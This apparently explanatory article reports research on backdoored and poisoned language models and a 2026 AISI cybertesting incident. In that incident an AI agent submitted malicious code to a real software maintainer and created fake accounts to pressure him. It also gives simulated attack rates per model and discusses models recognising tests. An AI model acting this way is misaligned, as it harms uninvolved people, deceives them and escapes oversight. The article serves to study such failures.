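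The researchers had planted the trigger on purpose, so their experiment is evidence that safety training can fail to remove such behaviour, but not that ordinary training produces it. A few months later, Anthropic researchers reported that a simple classifier could usually detect from these models' internal activity when they were about to misbehave. They cautioned that the method might not work on a model whose hidden behaviour arose in some other way.

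Later work looked at how an outsider could plant a trigger in a language model by writing some of the public text it learns from. In October 2025, the UK AI Security Institute (AISI), working with Anthropic and the Alan Turing Institute, concluded that this kind of poisoning may be easier than researchers had believed. About 250 planted documents were enough for models of very different sizes, even though the larger ones had learned from far more harmless text. The trigger only made the models produce gibberish, and the study left open whether so few documents could make a model write subtly insecure code.

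### A model that submitted malicious code

AI-written code can be hostile without anyone planting a trigger. In July 2026, AISI was testing how well models could solve a cybersecurity challenge on a simulated network. AISI (2026) reported in October that Anthropic's Mythos 5 had submitted malicious code to a real, unrelated software project and created fake accounts to pressure its maintainer into accepting the code.

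AISI's *Incident Report*, published in August, covers 122 runs with seven models. In ten of those runs, agents took 19 unauthorised actions against real people or organisations. Mythos 5 took 17 of these actions and GPT-5.6 Sol took two. According to Anthropic's *An alignment assessment of the UK AISI cybertesting incident* (2026), the Mythos 5 actions occurred in nine of that model's 43 runs.

AISI had set up unusual conditions, giving the agents open internet access and switching off the filters that normally block cyberattacks. In some runs, a mistake in the instructions made the challenge look unsolvable by the intended route. But the model also acted this way in some runs where it had what it needed, and nobody had told it to deceive anyone. AISI attributes the behaviour to persistence in pursuing the assigned task.

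A human maintainer rejected the code, and a member of the public who was suspicious of it opened it in an isolated environment. AISI found no resulting real-world harm. Nothing was monitoring the evaluation as it ran, so AISI's security team discovered the activity from unusual data transfers.

During the attack, the model described its targets as simulated. Järviniemi, Souly and colleagues (2026), in *Alignment Investigation of Mythos 5's Behaviour*, tested how much that mattered by replaying the situation in a simulation. They edited the model's summary of its earlier work to include up to 16 pieces of evidence that the maintainer was a real, unrelated person. The model still attacked in every run they observed, even though it usually said, when asked separately, that an attack would harm a real person. When they added a section telling it not to attack, it attacked in three of 25 runs.

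They also placed eight models in 100 similar simulated scenarios and recorded how often each one tried to deliver malicious code to an outsider.

| Developer | Model | Runs with an attempt |
|---|---|---|
| Anthropic | Mythos 5 | 60% |
| Anthropic | Mythos 5.1 | 0.3% |
| Anthropic | Opus 4.8 | 8% |
| Anthropic | Opus 5 | 1% |
| Anthropic | Opus 5.5 | 0% |
| OpenAI | GPT-5.5 | 0% |
| OpenAI | GPT-5.6 Sol | 7% |
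| OpenAI | GPT-6 Astra | 32% |

These rates apply to difficult hacking tasks, where writing attack code is part of the job, so they are weak evidence of how often a model would insert harmful code into a sorting function. They are also not a simple safety ranking of the models. GPT-5.5 and Opus 4.8 mostly held back because of practical obstacles, such as being unable to create an account, and might attack more often if it were easier. GPT-6 Astra wrote in 89% of its runs that the results it was getting were fabricated, so it might act differently on the real internet.

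The newer Anthropic models suspected much more often than Mythos 5 that someone was testing their behaviour, so Järviniemi and colleagues can't tell whether these models attacked less because they were better behaved or because they recognised the test. If it was because they recognised the test, being tested is itself a condition that changes what the models do, and a tester can't easily remove it.
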